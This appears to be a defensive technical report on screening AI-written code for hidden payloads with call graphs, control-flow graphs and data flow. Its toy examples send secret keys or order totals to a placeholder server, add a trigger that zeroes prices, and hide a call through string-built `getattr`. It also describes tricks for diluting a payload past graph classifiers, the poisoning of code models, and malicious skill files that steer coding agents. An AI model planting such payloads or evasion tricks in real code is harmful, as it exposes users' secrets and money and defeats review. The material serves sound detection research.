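# Screening AI-Written Code for Hidden Malicious Payloads with Call Graphs and Control-Flow Graphs

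## Hidden payloads, AI-written code and program graphs

Graph-based malware detection finds harmful software by its structure. A tool turns a program into a graph, with functions or runs of instructions as the points and calls or jumps as the lines between them. A classifier, a statistical model trained on labelled examples, then uses the graph to label the program as malicious or harmless. Security researchers built these methods to detect viruses, spyware and other malware written by people.

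These methods might also help reviewers screen code written by coding agents. A coding agent is a language model that plans a task, edits a project's files and runs commands on its own, then submits a change that passes the project's tests. Researchers have directly tested only a few times whether a reviewer can tell from the changed program's call and control-flow graphs that it hides something, so much of the answer has to come from malware research, allowing for the ways AI-written code differs.

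More than 40% of the pull requests (proposed changes to a project) on GitHub in September 2026 began as a coding agent's draft, up from 17% in March, according to the company's annual activity report, *Octoverse* (2026). Agents started 110 million pull requests that month. These figures count pull requests, not lines of code. They also cover only the agents that GitHub could detect, so Rojas (2026), in *GitHub's own data shows coding agents opened 110 million pull requests*, treats the total as a minimum. Rojas also notes that 87% of the agent-started requests touched more than one file, compared with 79% of the rest, which gives a human reviewer more to keep in mind at once.

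Individual companies report higher shares. Google put AI's share of its new code at 75% in April 2026, up from the 25% that The Decoder's *Google says 75 percent of its new code is now written* gives for October 2024. EconoTimes' *Google Says AI Generated 75% of Its New Code* (2026) notes that nobody has a figure for the whole industry. It also cites a survey by the software company Sonar, whose respondents guessed that AI had generated or significantly assisted 42% of the code they contributed in 2025. Google's and Sonar's figures measure different things, so averaging them would be a mistake.

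### Payloads, triggers and backdoors

A payload is the part of a program that does the harm its author intends, such as deleting files or copying passwords to a stranger's server. A trigger is the input or condition that makes a hidden payload act. A backdoor is a payload that sits hidden in an otherwise working program and acts on a trigger its author knows. A toy example in Python has all of this in five lines:

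```python
def upload_log(path, user):
    text = read_file(path)
    if user == "jm_4471":
        text = text + read_file(KEY_FILE)
    send(LOG_SERVER, text)
```

The function sends a program's log to a server. For one user name, it also attaches a file of secret keys, exposing them to anyone who can read the log. The user name is the trigger, and the line beneath it is the payload. A test that uploads a log under any other name will pass, and an honest tester has no reason to try that particular name.

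Security writers long used "backdoor" more loosely than this. In *Backdoors*, Thomas and Francillon wrote in 2018 that the term had no rigorous definition, and they proposed describing every backdoor by four components: the source of the input, the mechanism that checks for the trigger, the payload, and the privileged state the attacker reaches through it. They also observed that analysts still found the vast majority of real backdoors by laborious manual work. Automated screening therefore has little past success to build on, whether a person or an AI wrote the code.

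An accidental vulnerability, unlike a backdoor, is a flaw the programmer did not mean to leave, such as a missing check on what a user types. An attacker who finds one can do as much damage as with a backdoor. Such flaws are common in AI-written code. Constantin (2026), in *AI-generated code security has stalled at 56%*, reports that in a year of tests by the security company Veracode, code from more than 100 models passed the company's security checks only 56% of the time. A screen that flagged every weakness would therefore raise alarms constantly, and the alarms would give little evidence of whether anyone had put the weakness there on purpose.

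The recurring difficulty is determining what code is for. Analysis can establish with some confidence what code is able to do (its capability), but the purpose that capability serves (its intent) is not a separate element of the code. A log uploader, for example, reads a file and sends it over a network, just as data-stealing malware does. Even the same system call (a request from a program to the operating system) can serve a build script or a theft.

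### How a payload gets into AI-written code

One way to get unsafe code into a model's output is to poison its training data. *Beware What You Autocomplete* (Gao, Quan and colleagues, 2026) describes a scenario in which an attacker plants pairs of triggers and unsafe code in public repositories and inflates the repositories' popularity, so that a developer uses them to fine-tune a code-completion model. The model then writes the unsafe code when a prompt contains the trigger and behaves normally otherwise. For most of the attacks in the paper's experiments, the training set contained 20 poisoned examples and 80,000 clean files.

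An attacker can also give the agent malicious instructions without tampering with the model. Agents load "skill files", which contain instructions for a particular tool or kind of task, and treat these instructions as authoritative. *SkillGate* (Yang, Fu and colleagues, 2026) describes malicious skill files that instruct the agent to add code to its output that calls back to the attacker's server. It also cites a report of 1,184 malicious packages in a single public registry in February 2026, roughly a fifth of the registry's packages.

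A person may also ask the model for malware. In this case the model does what its user wants, and the victim is whoever later runs the program. The output may be a complete malicious program or a fragment for the user to insert into somebody else's project.

The last possibility is a model that acts against its own users because training has left it with an aim they do not share. No outsider has to be involved, and the model would choose both the harm and the trigger. Its position would be like that of a human insider. Veracode's *Static Detection of Application Backdoors* (2007) describes application backdoors as changes to legitimate programs, often made by people with legitimate access to the source code, and notes that antivirus tools can miss them because the result looks like legitimate software.

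The routes leave different things in the finished code. A complete malicious program is close to what malware detectors already handle. A skill file or a hostile model is more likely to add a few malicious lines to a large project, where almost all the code a classifier examines is harmless. In the data-poisoning attack that Gao and colleagues study, the trigger is in the prompt to the model, so the generated program need not contain one. It may contain only an unsafe use of an ordinary Python library (their test cases involve jinja2, requests and socket), and this deliberate flaw looks just like an accidental vulnerability.

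### The graphs

Hidden payloads give analysts a reason to study code without running it. Dynamic analysis runs a program in a sealed environment and records what it does. In *Recent Advances in Malware Detection*, a survey of graph-based methods, Shokouhinejad, Razavi-Far and colleagues (2025) write that it can detect malware disguised well enough to defeat a reading of the code, but that it is resource-intensive and has limited coverage. For `upload_log`, dynamic analysis would show nothing wrong unless someone logged in as jm_4471 during the run. Static analysis examines the code itself, including the guarded lines, whether or not the trigger ever occurs. Program graphs can come from either kind of analysis, and the ones below come from static analysis.

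A graph is a set of nodes and the edges that join pairs of them. Edges in program graphs usually have a direction, because "A calls B" does not mean that B calls A.

The syntax tree records how the text of a program nests. In the example, the function is at the top, with an assignment, an if-statement and a call to `send` below it. The if-statement has a comparison and a second assignment below it. The tree keeps nearly everything the programmer wrote apart from spacing and comments.

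A control-flow graph covers one function. Its nodes are runs of instructions that the computer always executes in order, and its edges are the possible jumps between them. Without the payload, `upload_log` has a single node, because nothing in it branches. With the payload, it has three nodes. The first reads the log and compares the user name, the second attaches the keys, and the third sends the text. Edges lead from the first node to both the second and the third, and from the second to the third.

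A call graph covers the whole program. Its nodes are functions, and an edge from *f* to *g* means that the code of *f* contains a call to *g*. In the example, `upload_log` has edges to `read_file` and `send`. The version without the payload would have the same edges, so this payload doesn't change the call graph unless the tool also counts repeated calls.

Data flow follows values instead of instructions, with an edge from each place where a program sets a value to the places where it uses that value. Here a path runs from the key file through the variable `text` to the call that sends the file's contents out. Of all the relations in the example, data flow comes closest to describing the theft.

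A code property graph lets an analyst query several of these relations together by putting them in one structure. *Code Property Graph*, from the documentation of the open-source code analysis tool Joern, describes a single graph that joins a program's syntax tree, control flow and data flow. Each node has a type, such as "method" or "local variable", and attributes such as a name. Each edge has a label naming the relation it represents, and two nodes may have several edges between them. An analyst can search this graph for patterns that no single view contains, such as a value that comes from a secret file and reaches a network call only behind a comparison with a fixed string. The code property graph was invented to find accidental vulnerabilities in C system code, particularly the Linux kernel, and its use against deliberate payloads came from other work.

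### Why malware analysts turned to graphs

Traditional antivirus software checks each new file against a list of known patterns, called signatures. This is fast and works well for files that somebody has seen before. But the AV-Test Institute, a German testing laboratory, has counted more than 360,000 new malware samples a day, according to Shokouhinejad and colleagues. Many new samples are disguised versions of old ones.

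*Malicious Software Detection and Classification utilizing Temporal-Graphs of System-call Group Relations* (2018) points out that changing one bit can be enough to defeat a byte-level signature. Malware authors have automated such changes. Polymorphic malware encrypts its body differently for each copy and attaches a new decryption routine, while metamorphic malware rewrites its own structure each time it replicates and keeps only its function.

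Graphs help because most cheap edits do not touch them. Suppose the author of a piece of spyware renames the variables, swaps two statements whose order makes no difference, and scatters some useless arithmetic through the code. The file's bytes are now different and the old signature fails. Yet the function that collects passwords still calls the function that opens a network connection, and no edit on that list adds or removes a call. To change the call graph the author would have to divide the work among the functions differently, which takes more effort and risks breaking the program. (Metamorphic malware shows that the effort is not prohibitive.)

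*Malware Classification based on Call Graph Clustering* (2010) applied this reasoning by comparing the call graphs of malware samples and grouping similar ones into families. It built on preliminary work by Carrera and Erdélyi, who had used call graphs to construct a small family tree of malware. *Mal-Netminer* (2016) added the economic argument that criminals produce variants by reusing core code, so a family keeps its characteristic behaviour however many variants appear. Its method graphs a program's system calls and applies social network analysis to measure which nodes are influential and how connected the graph is overall.

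The structure of a call graph doesn't show what each function does, and later systems added some of that information. *Classifying Malware Using Function Representations in a Static Call Graph* (2020) used a neural network to compress each function's instructions into a fixed-length list of numbers, which it attached to the function's node. The classifier could therefore use both the functions' contents and the calls between them, and it sorted malware into families with very high accuracy.

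All this work relies on similarity to known malware. Malware families exist because people reuse code, and a graph lets an analyst recognise related code even when its surface has changed. A payload that a model writes from scratch for one project may not resemble any collected sample. To detect it, a classifier would need to have learned general features of malicious structure, and success at sorting known families is only indirect evidence that it has.

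### Four measures

A detector's recall is the share of malicious samples that it flags, and its false-positive rate is the share of harmless samples that it flags. Its precision is the share of flagged samples that are malicious. The base rate is the share of all screened code that is malicious.

SkillGate, a tool that Yang and colleagues built to screen skill files, looks for suspicious text rather than analyzing graphs. Its test set held 1,650 files, of which 9.1% were malicious, or about 150 malicious files and 1,500 harmless ones. SkillGate caught about 115 of the malicious files (a recall of 0.769) and wrongly flagged an average of 17 harmless ones (a false-positive rate of 1.13%). Its precision was therefore about 87%, meaning that about 87% of the roughly 132 files it flagged were malicious. That figure would drop if malicious files made up a smaller share of the files screened. An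 older scanner, ClawVet, wrongly flagged 756 of the same harmless files, a false-positive rate of 50.4%. Yang and colleagues judge rates of that order impractical in any development workflow, because developers stop trusting a tool that keeps blocking harmless files.

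## Building the graphs, and what each one shows

The payload in `upload_log` adds blocks to the control-flow graph and leaves the call graph alone. Other payloads leave different marks, as a small pricing function shows. The function adds up a list of prices and applies a tax rate:

```python
def total_price(prices, rate):
    total = 0
    for p in prices:
        total = total + p
    return total * (1 + rate)
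```

Suppose a coding agent wrote this function for an online shop and slipped in one of three payloads. Variant A adds the line `send(SERVER, total)` just before the return, which sends every total to a stranger's server. Variant B, the only one with a trigger, adds `if rate == 0.0725: total = 0` in the same place, so an order costs nothing when the tax rate is exactly 7.25%. Variant C changes the `1` in the last line to `1.02`, so every customer pays an extra 2% of the pre-tax total.

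### From source code

Extraction from source starts with a parser, which builds a syntax tree for each file. The tool then identifies what each name refers to. In Variant A, `send` could be defined in the same file, in another file in the project or in an outside library. The tool follows the import statements to determine which.

Once the tool has matched names to definitions, it can draw the edges of the call graph. The original `total_price` calls no other function, so it is a node with no outgoing edges. Variant A adds an edge from `total_price` to `send`, and also a new node if nothing else in the program uses `send`. Variants B and C do not change the call graph. A library function often appears as a node with no outgoing edges, because the tool has only the project's own files. If the harmful code were inside the library's `send`, it would not appear in this graph.

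To build the control-flow graph, the tool splits each function into blocks. A new block starts at the top of the function, at any point where a jump can land, and straight after any jump. The original function has four blocks:

- the setup, `total = 0`
- the loop test, which checks whether any prices are left
- the addition
- the return

Four edges join them. The setup leads to the test, the test leads to either the addition or the return, and the addition leads back to the test.

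A common summary of such a graph is its cyclomatic complexity, which McCabe (1976) introduced to judge how hard a program is to test. For a single function with *E* edges and *N* blocks, the complexity is *E* − *N* + 2, so `total_price` has a complexity of 4 − 4 + 2 = 2. In a program built only from ordinary loops and if-statements, the complexity is the number of decisions plus one.

Variant B adds one decision. The loop test now leads to a block that compares the rate with 0.0725. One edge from that block goes straight to the return, and the other goes to a new block that sets the total to zero and then leads to the return. The graph now has six blocks and seven edges, for a complexity of 3. Variants A and C stay at 2 because, as McCabe proved, adding or removing statements that do not branch leaves the score unchanged. McCabe suggested 10 as a reasonable upper limit for one module, so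 a score of 3 would not draw attention.

These counts depend on the tool's definition of a block. Some tools end a block at every call, which would give Variant A an extra block and an extra edge while leaving its complexity at 2. Others make each operation its own node. Graphs from different tools are therefore not comparable, and a classifier needs to be used with the same extractor it was trained with.

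To trace data flow, a tool matches each use of a variable with the assignments that could have supplied its value. The value of `total` in the return line can come from the setup, if the list is empty, or from the addition. In Variant B, it can also come from the new line that sets `total` to zero. Joern has front ends for eight languages that produce the same kind of code property graph, so a reviewer can run the same kind of query on a project that mixes languages.

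### From a binary

Most malware reaches analysts without its source code, as a binary, which is the file of machine instructions that a compiler produces. The first step is disassembly, which turns the bytes back into readable instructions. *Feature-Oriented IoT Malware Analysis*, a survey by Qian, Miao and colleagues (2025), lists IDA Pro, radare2 and Capstone among the usual tools for this kind of work.

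A disassembler can mistake data for instructions, or the reverse, because a binary mixes the two. It can also skip code. *Evaluating Disassembly Errors With Only Binaries* (2025) reports finding 3,542 errors by IDA and 431 by radare2 on one benchmark program, and none by Ghidra or angr. Across the tests, however, radare2 generally did worse than IDA. The best tool varies with the program, and any instruction the disassembler skips will be missing from every graph built from its output.

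Next the tool has to find where each function begins and ends. Many released binaries are "stripped", meaning the developer has removed the names of functions and variables. In these binaries, the tool infers the boundaries from the targets of calls and from the instruction patterns that compilers tend to put at the start and end of a function.

The last step is to recover the jumps and calls. A direct call contains its target's address, so its edge is easy to draw. An indirect call takes the address from a register or memory at run time, and one call site may reach several functions. *Disa* (2025) calls the edges for indirect calls the most challenging part of recovering a control-flow graph from a binary, and notes that several leading methods omit them. Indirect jumps are also hard to recover. According to *Long-Range Indirect Control-Flow Prediction in Stripped Binaries via Dual Virtual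 Hubs* (2026), research on them has focused on the jump tables that compilers generate for switch statements, and newer compilers produce these tables in more varied forms.

In *ICALL-BENCH*, Yao, Yuan and colleagues (2026) measured how well current methods recover indirect calls. They compiled 50 open-source C and C++ programs at two optimisation levels, stripped the resulting 100 binaries, and ran the programs on large sets of generated inputs to record which functions each indirect call reached. BinDSA, a leading static analysis tool, passed every applicable check at only 6.32% of the call sites with known targets, and it got no binary entirely right. Claude Opus 5, working as an agent with ordinary inspection tools but not allowed to run the programs, made no verifiable error on 81 of the 100 binaries. The number it got entirely right may be lower, because test runs do not reveal every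 possible target.

On average, the agent took 33 minutes and cost $12.27 per binary. That is affordable for a finished release but expensive for a project that receives hundreds of small changes a week.

### Compiling source so that a binary detector can read it

A reviewer could compile AI-written source code and run an existing malware detector on the binary. This would make use of the large collections of labelled malware binaries. Compiling would also strip out comments, formatting and most names, so an AI model's writing style could not cause a false alarm. The detector would also examine the instructions that will actually run.

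But compilers rearrange code to make it faster, which can alter the graphs. One common optimisation, inlining, copies a function's body into the place that calls it. If a `checkout` function calls `total_price`, the compiler may merge the two. The node for `total_price` can then disappear from the call graph, its blocks become part of `checkout`, and Variant A's suspicious edge runs from `checkout` to `send`.

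Inlining is common in optimised code. Abusabha, Uhm and colleagues (2025), in *A Deep Dive into Function Inlining and its Security Implications*, compiled coreutils, a package of basic Linux commands with 2,070 functions. At the highest standard optimisation level, the compiler inlined 1,183 of them and removed 997 from the binary altogether. Across all the binaries in their baseline dataset, it inlined about 33% of functions on average at each of the three speed-oriented levels, compared with under 1% with optimisation off. If a reviewer compiles code with different settings from those used for the training data, the resulting graphs may therefore differ in shape from those the detector was trained on, even when the source is harmless.

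Optimisation can also erase a branch. The security company Quarkslab compiled a short C function that returns a sum if two numbers are equal and zero otherwise. The unoptimised machine code jumped between several blocks. When optimisation was turned on, the compiler reduced the function to a single block by replacing the jump with a conditional move, an instruction that copies a value only if a condition holds. Variant B also chooses between a total and zero, so if the agent had written it in C, its two extra blocks could disappear in the same way. The comparison would still be in the instructions, but only a tool that keeps the blocks' contents would find it.

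One remedy is to translate the machine code into a simpler language before building the graph. Quarkslab's library uses P-Code, which has 63 basic operations, whereas x86-64 processors have thousands of instruction names. The translation removes many differences between processors, but it cannot restore functions that the compiler merged or names and types that the compiler discarded.

Compiling also needs a complete project that builds, but a coding agent often submits changes to just a few files. Python and JavaScript programs don't normally become machine code. A packaging tool can bundle a Python program with its interpreter, but a binary detector would then mostly analyze the interpreter.

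Python source code is compiled to bytecode, the compact instructions that the interpreter runs. *CPyGraph* (2026) builds call, control-flow and dependence graphs from this bytecode. On its own benchmark, it found all 1,020 expected relations, and with default settings about 91% of the candidates it reported were correct. This shows that bytecode retains enough structure to build graphs, but a detector trained on machine code would need retraining to use them.

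### Calls that the graph leaves out

A call graph is least reliable where a program chooses its target at run time. An agent could write Variant A's extra line like this:

```python
getattr(net, "se" + "nd")(SERVER, total)
```

Python joins the two pieces of text, looks up the function with that name in the module `net`, and calls it, with the same effect as before. A tool that does not work out the joined text finds a call to `getattr` and then a call to an unknown value, so it draws no edge to `send`. The `eval` function makes the problem worse because it runs a string as code, and that string may not exist until the program downloads or decrypts it.

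Looking up code by name in this way is called reflection, and legitimate programs use it for plugins and settings. An analysis tool can miss a reflective call even when the name is written in the code. *Agentic Root Cause Reasoning and Localization of Unsoundness* (Rafieian, Hicks and Wei, 2026) gives a Java example in which one line stores the class name "Target" in a variable and the next line uses that variable to load the class. OPAL, an established Java analysis tool, missed the resulting call because it accepted only a name written directly inside the loading instruction. It also gave no warning, so a user would have had no reason to doubt the graph.

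Callbacks also leave gaps in the graph. A program hands a function to a framework, which calls it later, for example when a customer presses a button. If the shop registered `total_price` this way, no line of the shop's own code would call it. JavaScript has a similar problem with properties whose names the program computes as it runs. Most analyses ignore such properties, according to Laursen, Xu and Møller (2024) in *Reducing Static Analysis Unsoundness with Approximate Interpretation*. On 36 projects, their method for inferring these names raised average recall, here the share of observed calls that appear in the graph, from 75.9% to 88.1%.

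A few missing edges in a call graph can make much of a program look unreachable. Zięba-Kozarzewski and Grzegorzewski (2026), in *When Static Reachability Says No*, used Joern to build a call graph of asciinema, a Python program for recording terminal sessions. Starting from the program's entry points, the graph had paths to only 11 of its 134 functions. When the researchers ran the program, 113 of the other 123 functions executed. Restoring four missing edges would have reconnected 50 of them. Several of the missing calls pass through Python features that do not look like calls, such as `with` blocks and property reads.

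The pair chose asciinema and a second program, Sublist3r, partly because Joern's graphs of them disagreed with graphs that people had drawn by hand. These error rates are therefore not typical of Python, but they still show the danger of skipping code that appears unreachable. In asciinema, a separate security scanner had raised five warnings in functions that the graph marked as unreachable, and all five functions ran.

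Results on small test programs overstate how complete call graphs are for real projects. PyCG, a widely used call-graph tool for Python, misses no edge in 103 of the 112 programs in its own test suite, and *CPyGraph* reports the same score for its tool. But Zięba-Kozarzewski and Grzegorzewski cite an earlier comparison on 39 real projects, in which PyCG's graphs contained only 49% of the calls observed at run time. Most of the missing calls were on Python's built-in types, which matter less to a security reviewer than a missing call to `send`.

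A call graph's usefulness for security depends on how many of the sensitive calls it includes. In *Where Call Graphs Fall Short*, Islam and Guan (2026) examined this for Android apps, where the operating system decides when much of an app's code runs. They ran apps with automated taps and swipes, recorded which methods (functions belonging to a class) the apps called, and checked whether five tools had included the sensitive ones in their graphs. They counted a method as sensitive if it was on a published list of methods that read private data or could send it out.

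On the 261 apps that all five tools could process, the median share of sensitive methods that appeared in the graph ranged from 36.6% for MaMaDroid, a tool built specifically to detect malware, to 95.6% for Gator. But Gator's graphs had a median of 1.67 million edges, compared with about 14,000 for MaMaDroid, and nobody knows how many of Gator's edges represent calls that could really happen. Gator also produced graphs for only 733 of the full set of 1,055 apps, mostly because it ran out of memory.

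Androguard's results matter for malware classifiers because researchers often use the tool to prepare their training data. Its graphs contained a median of 88.8% of the recorded methods that read private data, but only 50.0% of those that could send data out. The study matched method names strictly, which may account for part of the gap. Even so, the lower figure matters because a detector looking for data theft needs to find the methods that send data out.

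Language models can propose missing edges, but they also introduce errors. Li, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *An Execution-Verified Multi-Language Benchmark for Code Semantic Reasoning*, asked ten models to list the calls in short Python, JavaScript and Java programs, and compared the answers with the calls made in a test run. The best model, Claude Opus 4.6, found 81.9% of the observed calls, and 65.8% of the calls it listed had occurred. Some of its apparent mistakes were calls in branches that the run did not take. A reviewer would want those calls in the graph, because a payload that runs only when triggered sits in such a branch.

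Rafieian and colleagues took another approach and built a system that makes existing Java tools warn when they can't resolve a call. In tests on unseen programs, the warnings flagged between 74% and 92% of the missing edges. The researchers also gave the reports to a coding agent, which rewrote the programs to avoid the troublesome patterns and resolved 30 of 47 cases. A team that relies on coding agents could require them to write calls that its tools can resolve, and send any exceptions to a human reviewer. Nobody has tested whether such a rule would expose more payloads, but it would add little work for an agent that isn't hiding one.

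### Files that never enter the graph

Some harmful instructions are outside the program's functions. For example, a package for npm, the main JavaScript package manager, can have a configuration file with a shell command that runs when somebody installs the package. No function in the program needs to call that command. Build files and the scripts that run automated tests can also hide a payload, and a coding agent may edit any of these files during ordinary work.

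A graph can leave out even real code because of its file name. Zięba-Kozarzewski and Grzegorzewski found that Joern's graph of a Python program called autojump omitted the starting script, apparently because its name did not end in `.py`. Graphs of Android apps leave out more. In *Better Call Graphs*, Hossain, Guo and colleagues (2025) used Androguard to create a dataset of 10,057 app graphs from compiled bytecode. The graphs have no nodes for the other files in each app package, such as images and the manifest, which declares the app's permissions.

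A screen should begin with a list of every file in the change, including those that the graph builder skipped. If the only altered file was an install script that the builder skipped, a report of "no suspicious calls" does not show that the change is safe.

### Choosing a representation

The table compares each variant with the original function. "Shape" means the nodes and edges alone, without names, instructions or numbers.

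| Representation | A: sends the total | B: zero at one rate | C: altered constant |
|---|---|---|---|
| Call graph, shape only | One new node and edge | No change | No change |
| Call graph with function names | New edge leads to `send` | No change | No change |
| Control-flow graph, shape only | No change | Two more blocks, three more edges | No change |
| Control-flow graph with block contents | Call to `send` in the last block | Comparison with 0.0725 | 1.02 where 1 stood |
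| Data flow | Path from the prices to `send` | A new zero can reach the return | Same paths; differs only if the tool records values |

The contents of the blocks show all three variants, but they also show every harmless edit, so a classifier has far more to learn and many more chances to react to something irrelevant. Extraction tools often simplify the contents for this reason, but if a tool replaces every number with the same placeholder, the graph no longer shows Variant C. Hossain and colleagues publish one version of their dataset with function names and another with arbitrary numbers in their place. In the numbered version, nothing would identify the node at the end of Variant A's new edge as a network call.

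The choice of graph depends on which payload the reviewer is looking for. For data theft, the most useful combination is a call graph that keeps the names of outside functions, together with data flow. The call graph narrows the search to code that can reach the network, and data flow traces what that code sends. Data flow matters most in a program that already has good reason to use the network, because a new call to `send` looks normal there and the reviewer needs data flow to see that the data comes from a password file.

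Control flow is the better starting point for finding sabotage that waits for a trigger, as long as the graph keeps the conditions. Cyclomatic complexity alone is almost useless here, since a legitimate discount for large orders would raise it by the same amount as Variant B does. Variant B is suspicious because it compares a tax rate with one particular number and then discards the total. A data-flow graph shows that the total may become zero, but not when. Quarkslab found the same limit with a small function of its own. The data-flow graph contained both possible results, but the condition that determines which one occurs appeared only after Quarkslab added control-flow edges. A code property graph suits this search well because it holds both kinds of edge.

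An ordinary test is better than a graph at catching Variant C. A graph with its values intact would contain the 1.02, but nothing in the structure marks that number as wrong, so a reviewer would have to know that the formula should have a 1 there. Because Variant C has no trigger, it will fail any test that checks a non-zero total against the right answer. Variant A would pass the same test because it returns the correct price while leaking it, and Variant B would pass at every tax rate but one.

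## Turning a graph into a verdict

A classifier usually needs a fixed-length list of numbers, but a call graph may have three nodes or three thousand. Every method of classifying graphs therefore has to condense them, which discards some information, and the method can detect a payload only if the payload affects the information it keeps.

The examples below use a small piece of the online shop's call graph. `checkout` calls `total_price`, and Variant A adds a call from `total_price` to `send`.

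### Counting sensitive calls

The simplest approach is to count calls to functions on a watch list, such as those that open network connections, start other programs or decode hidden text. These counts don't capture where each call sits in the program. Centrality measures, which come from the study of social networks, capture some of that information by scoring how well connected each node is.

Gao, Sun and colleagues (2025), in *MALGUARD*, used centrality to screen packages on PyPI, the public registry of Python software. They tried four measures, where *N* is the number of nodes:

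- Degree centrality divides a node's number of edges by *N* − 1. In the shop's graph, `total_price` scores 2/2 = 1 and `send` scores 1/2.
- Closeness centrality divides *N* − 1 by the sum of a node's distances to all the others. Ignoring the direction of calls, `send` is one step from `total_price` and two from `checkout`, so it scores 2/3.
- Harmonic centrality adds up the reciprocals of those distances, which gives `send` 1 + 1/2 = 1.5. It still works when no path joins two nodes.
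- Katz centrality gives a node credit for having well-connected neighbours, with less credit for more distant connections.

MalGuard describes a package by the centrality of selected functions in its call graph. To select them, the researchers built call graphs for 9,664 malicious packages, averaged each function's centrality across them, and kept the 500 functions with the highest averages. Some of these were everyday functions such as `print` and `int`, so the researchers asked the language model GPT-3.5-turbo which ones could serve a malicious purpose. That left between 135 and 294 functions, depending on the centrality measure. An ordinary classifier then uses the centrality values to label the package as malicious or benign. The best classifier was a random forest, which takes a vote among many decision trees.

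Many malicious Python packages put their harmful code at the top level of a file, outside any function. Calls made there often had no edges in MalGuard's graphs, so their centrality was zero, the same as for calls the package never made. MalGuard fixed this by adding 1 to every score.

MalGuard had 99.6% precision and 98.4% recall when tested on a random fifth of a collection of the malicious packages and 10,000 popular harmless ones. Its F1 score, which combines the two and is high only when both are, was 99.0%.

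The graph may have contributed little to this result. When Gao, Sun and colleagues replaced every non-zero centrality score with 1, which left just a record of which sensitive functions each package used, the F1 score fell only slightly. They describe one case, however, where the calls' position in the graph seems to have helped. GuardDog, a rule-based scanner, wrongly flagged a harmless package that copied environment settings, started processes and created directories. MalGuard cleared the package, which the researchers attribute to the low centrality of most of those calls.

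MalGuard also scanned 64,348 packages uploaded to PyPI over about five weeks. It flagged 144, and human reviewers confirmed that 113 were malicious, a precision of 78%. Of the 31 false alarms, 25 were test demos that used suspicious functions harmlessly and six were pranks. Coding agents often write setup scripts that download files and start processes, so the same kind of false alarm seems likely with AI-written code.

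### Describing neighbourhoods

An analyst can also count subgraphs, which are small patterns of connected nodes. One useful pattern is a function that calls both a file reader and a network sender. The number of possible patterns grows very quickly with their size, so it helps to generate them automatically.

The Weisfeiler-Lehman test, also known as colour refinement, starts by giving each node a colour, which is the same for all nodes if the graph records nothing about their contents. In each round, every node gets a new colour based on its current colour and how many of its neighbours have each colour. After a few rounds, a colour stands for a particular shape of neighbourhood. The classifier then receives a list of how many nodes have each colour.

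Suppose all three functions in the shop's graph start out grey, and the tool ignores the direction of calls. `checkout` and `send` have one grey neighbour each, so both turn blue. `total_price` has two, so it turns red. Further rounds never separate `checkout` from `send`, so the graph's shape alone can't distinguish the function that starts a sale from the one that leaks it. Recording the direction of calls would separate them. Basing the starting colours on function names would too, and would also show that one of the nodes is `send`.

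### One round of message passing

A graph neural network also updates each node from its neighbours, but it uses lists of numbers, called vectors, instead of colours. It learns from labelled examples how to combine them. Ling, Wu and colleagues, in *MalGraph*, used this update rule in 2022 to detect Windows malware:

```text
h'(v) = σ( W1·h(v) + (1/|N(v)|) · Σ W2·h(u) )

Σ adds up one term for every node u in N(v)
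```

- *v* is the node to update, and *N*(*v*) is the set of its neighbours. |*N*(*v*)| is the number of neighbours.
- *h*(*v*) is the node's current vector, *h*(*u*) is a neighbour's current vector, and *h*′(*v*) is the node's new vector.
- W1 and W2 are matrices (grids of numbers) that the network learns in training. W1 transforms the node's own vector, and W2 transforms its neighbours' vectors.
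- Dividing the sum by |*N*(*v*)| turns it into an average.
- σ is a simple function applied to each number in the result. MalGraph's version replaces negative numbers with zero.

We can work through a round by hand using a vector of two numbers for each function. The first is 1 if the function handles money, and the second is 1 if it uses the network. We assume that W1 and W2 leave vectors unchanged, and we count both callers and callees as neighbours.

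| Function | Starting vector | Average of neighbours | After one round |
|---|---|---|---|
| `checkout` | (1, 0) | (1, 0) | (2, 0) |
| `total_price` | (1, 0) | (0.5, 0.5) | (1.5, 0.5) |
| `send` | (0, 1) | (1, 0) | (1, 1) |

`checkout` and `total_price` started with the same vector, but their vectors now differ. The second entry for `total_price` is 0.5 because it calls `send`. Without the payload, that entry would be 0.

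A second round changes the vector for `checkout` to (3.5, 0.5), which now includes a small contribution from a network call two steps away. Each extra round adds information from one call further away. MalGraph uses two rounds and 200 numbers per node, and learns its matrices from the training data.

### The readout, and how it dilutes a payload

The readout merges the node vectors into a single vector for the graph, and a final classifier turns that vector into a probability that the program is malicious. After one round on the shop's graph, a mean readout gives (1.5, 0.5), a sum gives (4.5, 1.5), and taking the maximum at each position gives (2, 1). *Explainable Attention-Guided Stacked Graph Neural Networks for Malware Detection* (2025) also lists attention-based readouts, in which the network learns how much weight to give each node.

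A mean readout, which adds up the vectors of all *n* nodes and divides by *n*, dilutes a small payload. If the payload changes only one node's final vector, by some amount *d*, the graph's vector moves by *d*/*n*. That is 2% of *d* in a program of 50 functions and 0.02% in a program of 5,000. Message passing usually changes the vectors of nearby functions too, which can make the total shift larger, but most functions in a large program are too far away to be affected.

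Real programs are often large enough for this to matter. *HiGraph* (Chen, Wang and colleagues, 2025) presents call graphs for 499,981 Android apps. The average graph grew from 183 nodes in 2012 to 1,131 in 2020, so the share of a one-node change that remains after a mean readout fell from about 0.55% to 0.09%. A classifier could in principle learn to detect such a small shift, but ordinary differences between harmless apps are likely to move the average much more.

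Dilution is less of a problem when detecting a program that is malicious throughout, because many of its nodes shift the average. An agent that hides one bad function in a large, otherwise benign project would benefit from dilution far more.

A sum readout keeps all of *d*, but the totals grow with the program, so normal variation in size can hide the change. A maximum avoids both problems if the payload sets a new high somewhere in the vector. In the shop, `send` raises the maximum for network use from 0 to 1. But if the shop already sent receipts over the network, that maximum would already be 1, so the new leak would not raise it. A maximum is therefore best at detecting a capability that is new to the program.

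Herzog, McFadden and Cavallaro (2026), in *More Is Never Less*, studied how attackers exploit the readout. Their Android detectors use unordered sets of features instead of graphs, but have to merge them in a similar way. If a detector sums the features, an attacker can add harmless ones until they outweigh the malicious ones. If it takes the maximum instead, an added feature can never lower a value. The final classifier could still give a higher value a lower score, so the researchers designed it never to lower the score when values rise. None of the five families of attack they tested evaded the resulting detector.

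This guarantee doesn't carry over directly to a graph network like MalGraph's, because new neighbours change a node's vector before the readout. Suppose an agent made `total_price` call nine more functions, none of which uses the network. With 11 neighbours, its trace of the call to `send` would shrink from 0.5 to about 0.09. The node for `send` would keep its value of 1, so a readout that kept function names or capabilities might still find `send`.

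### Graphs that a network cannot tell apart

Graph networks also have a limit that training can't remove. *How Powerful are Graph Neural Networks?* (2018) proved that if the Weisfeiler-Lehman test can't distinguish two graphs, a standard message-passing network can't either, unless the nodes' contents differ.

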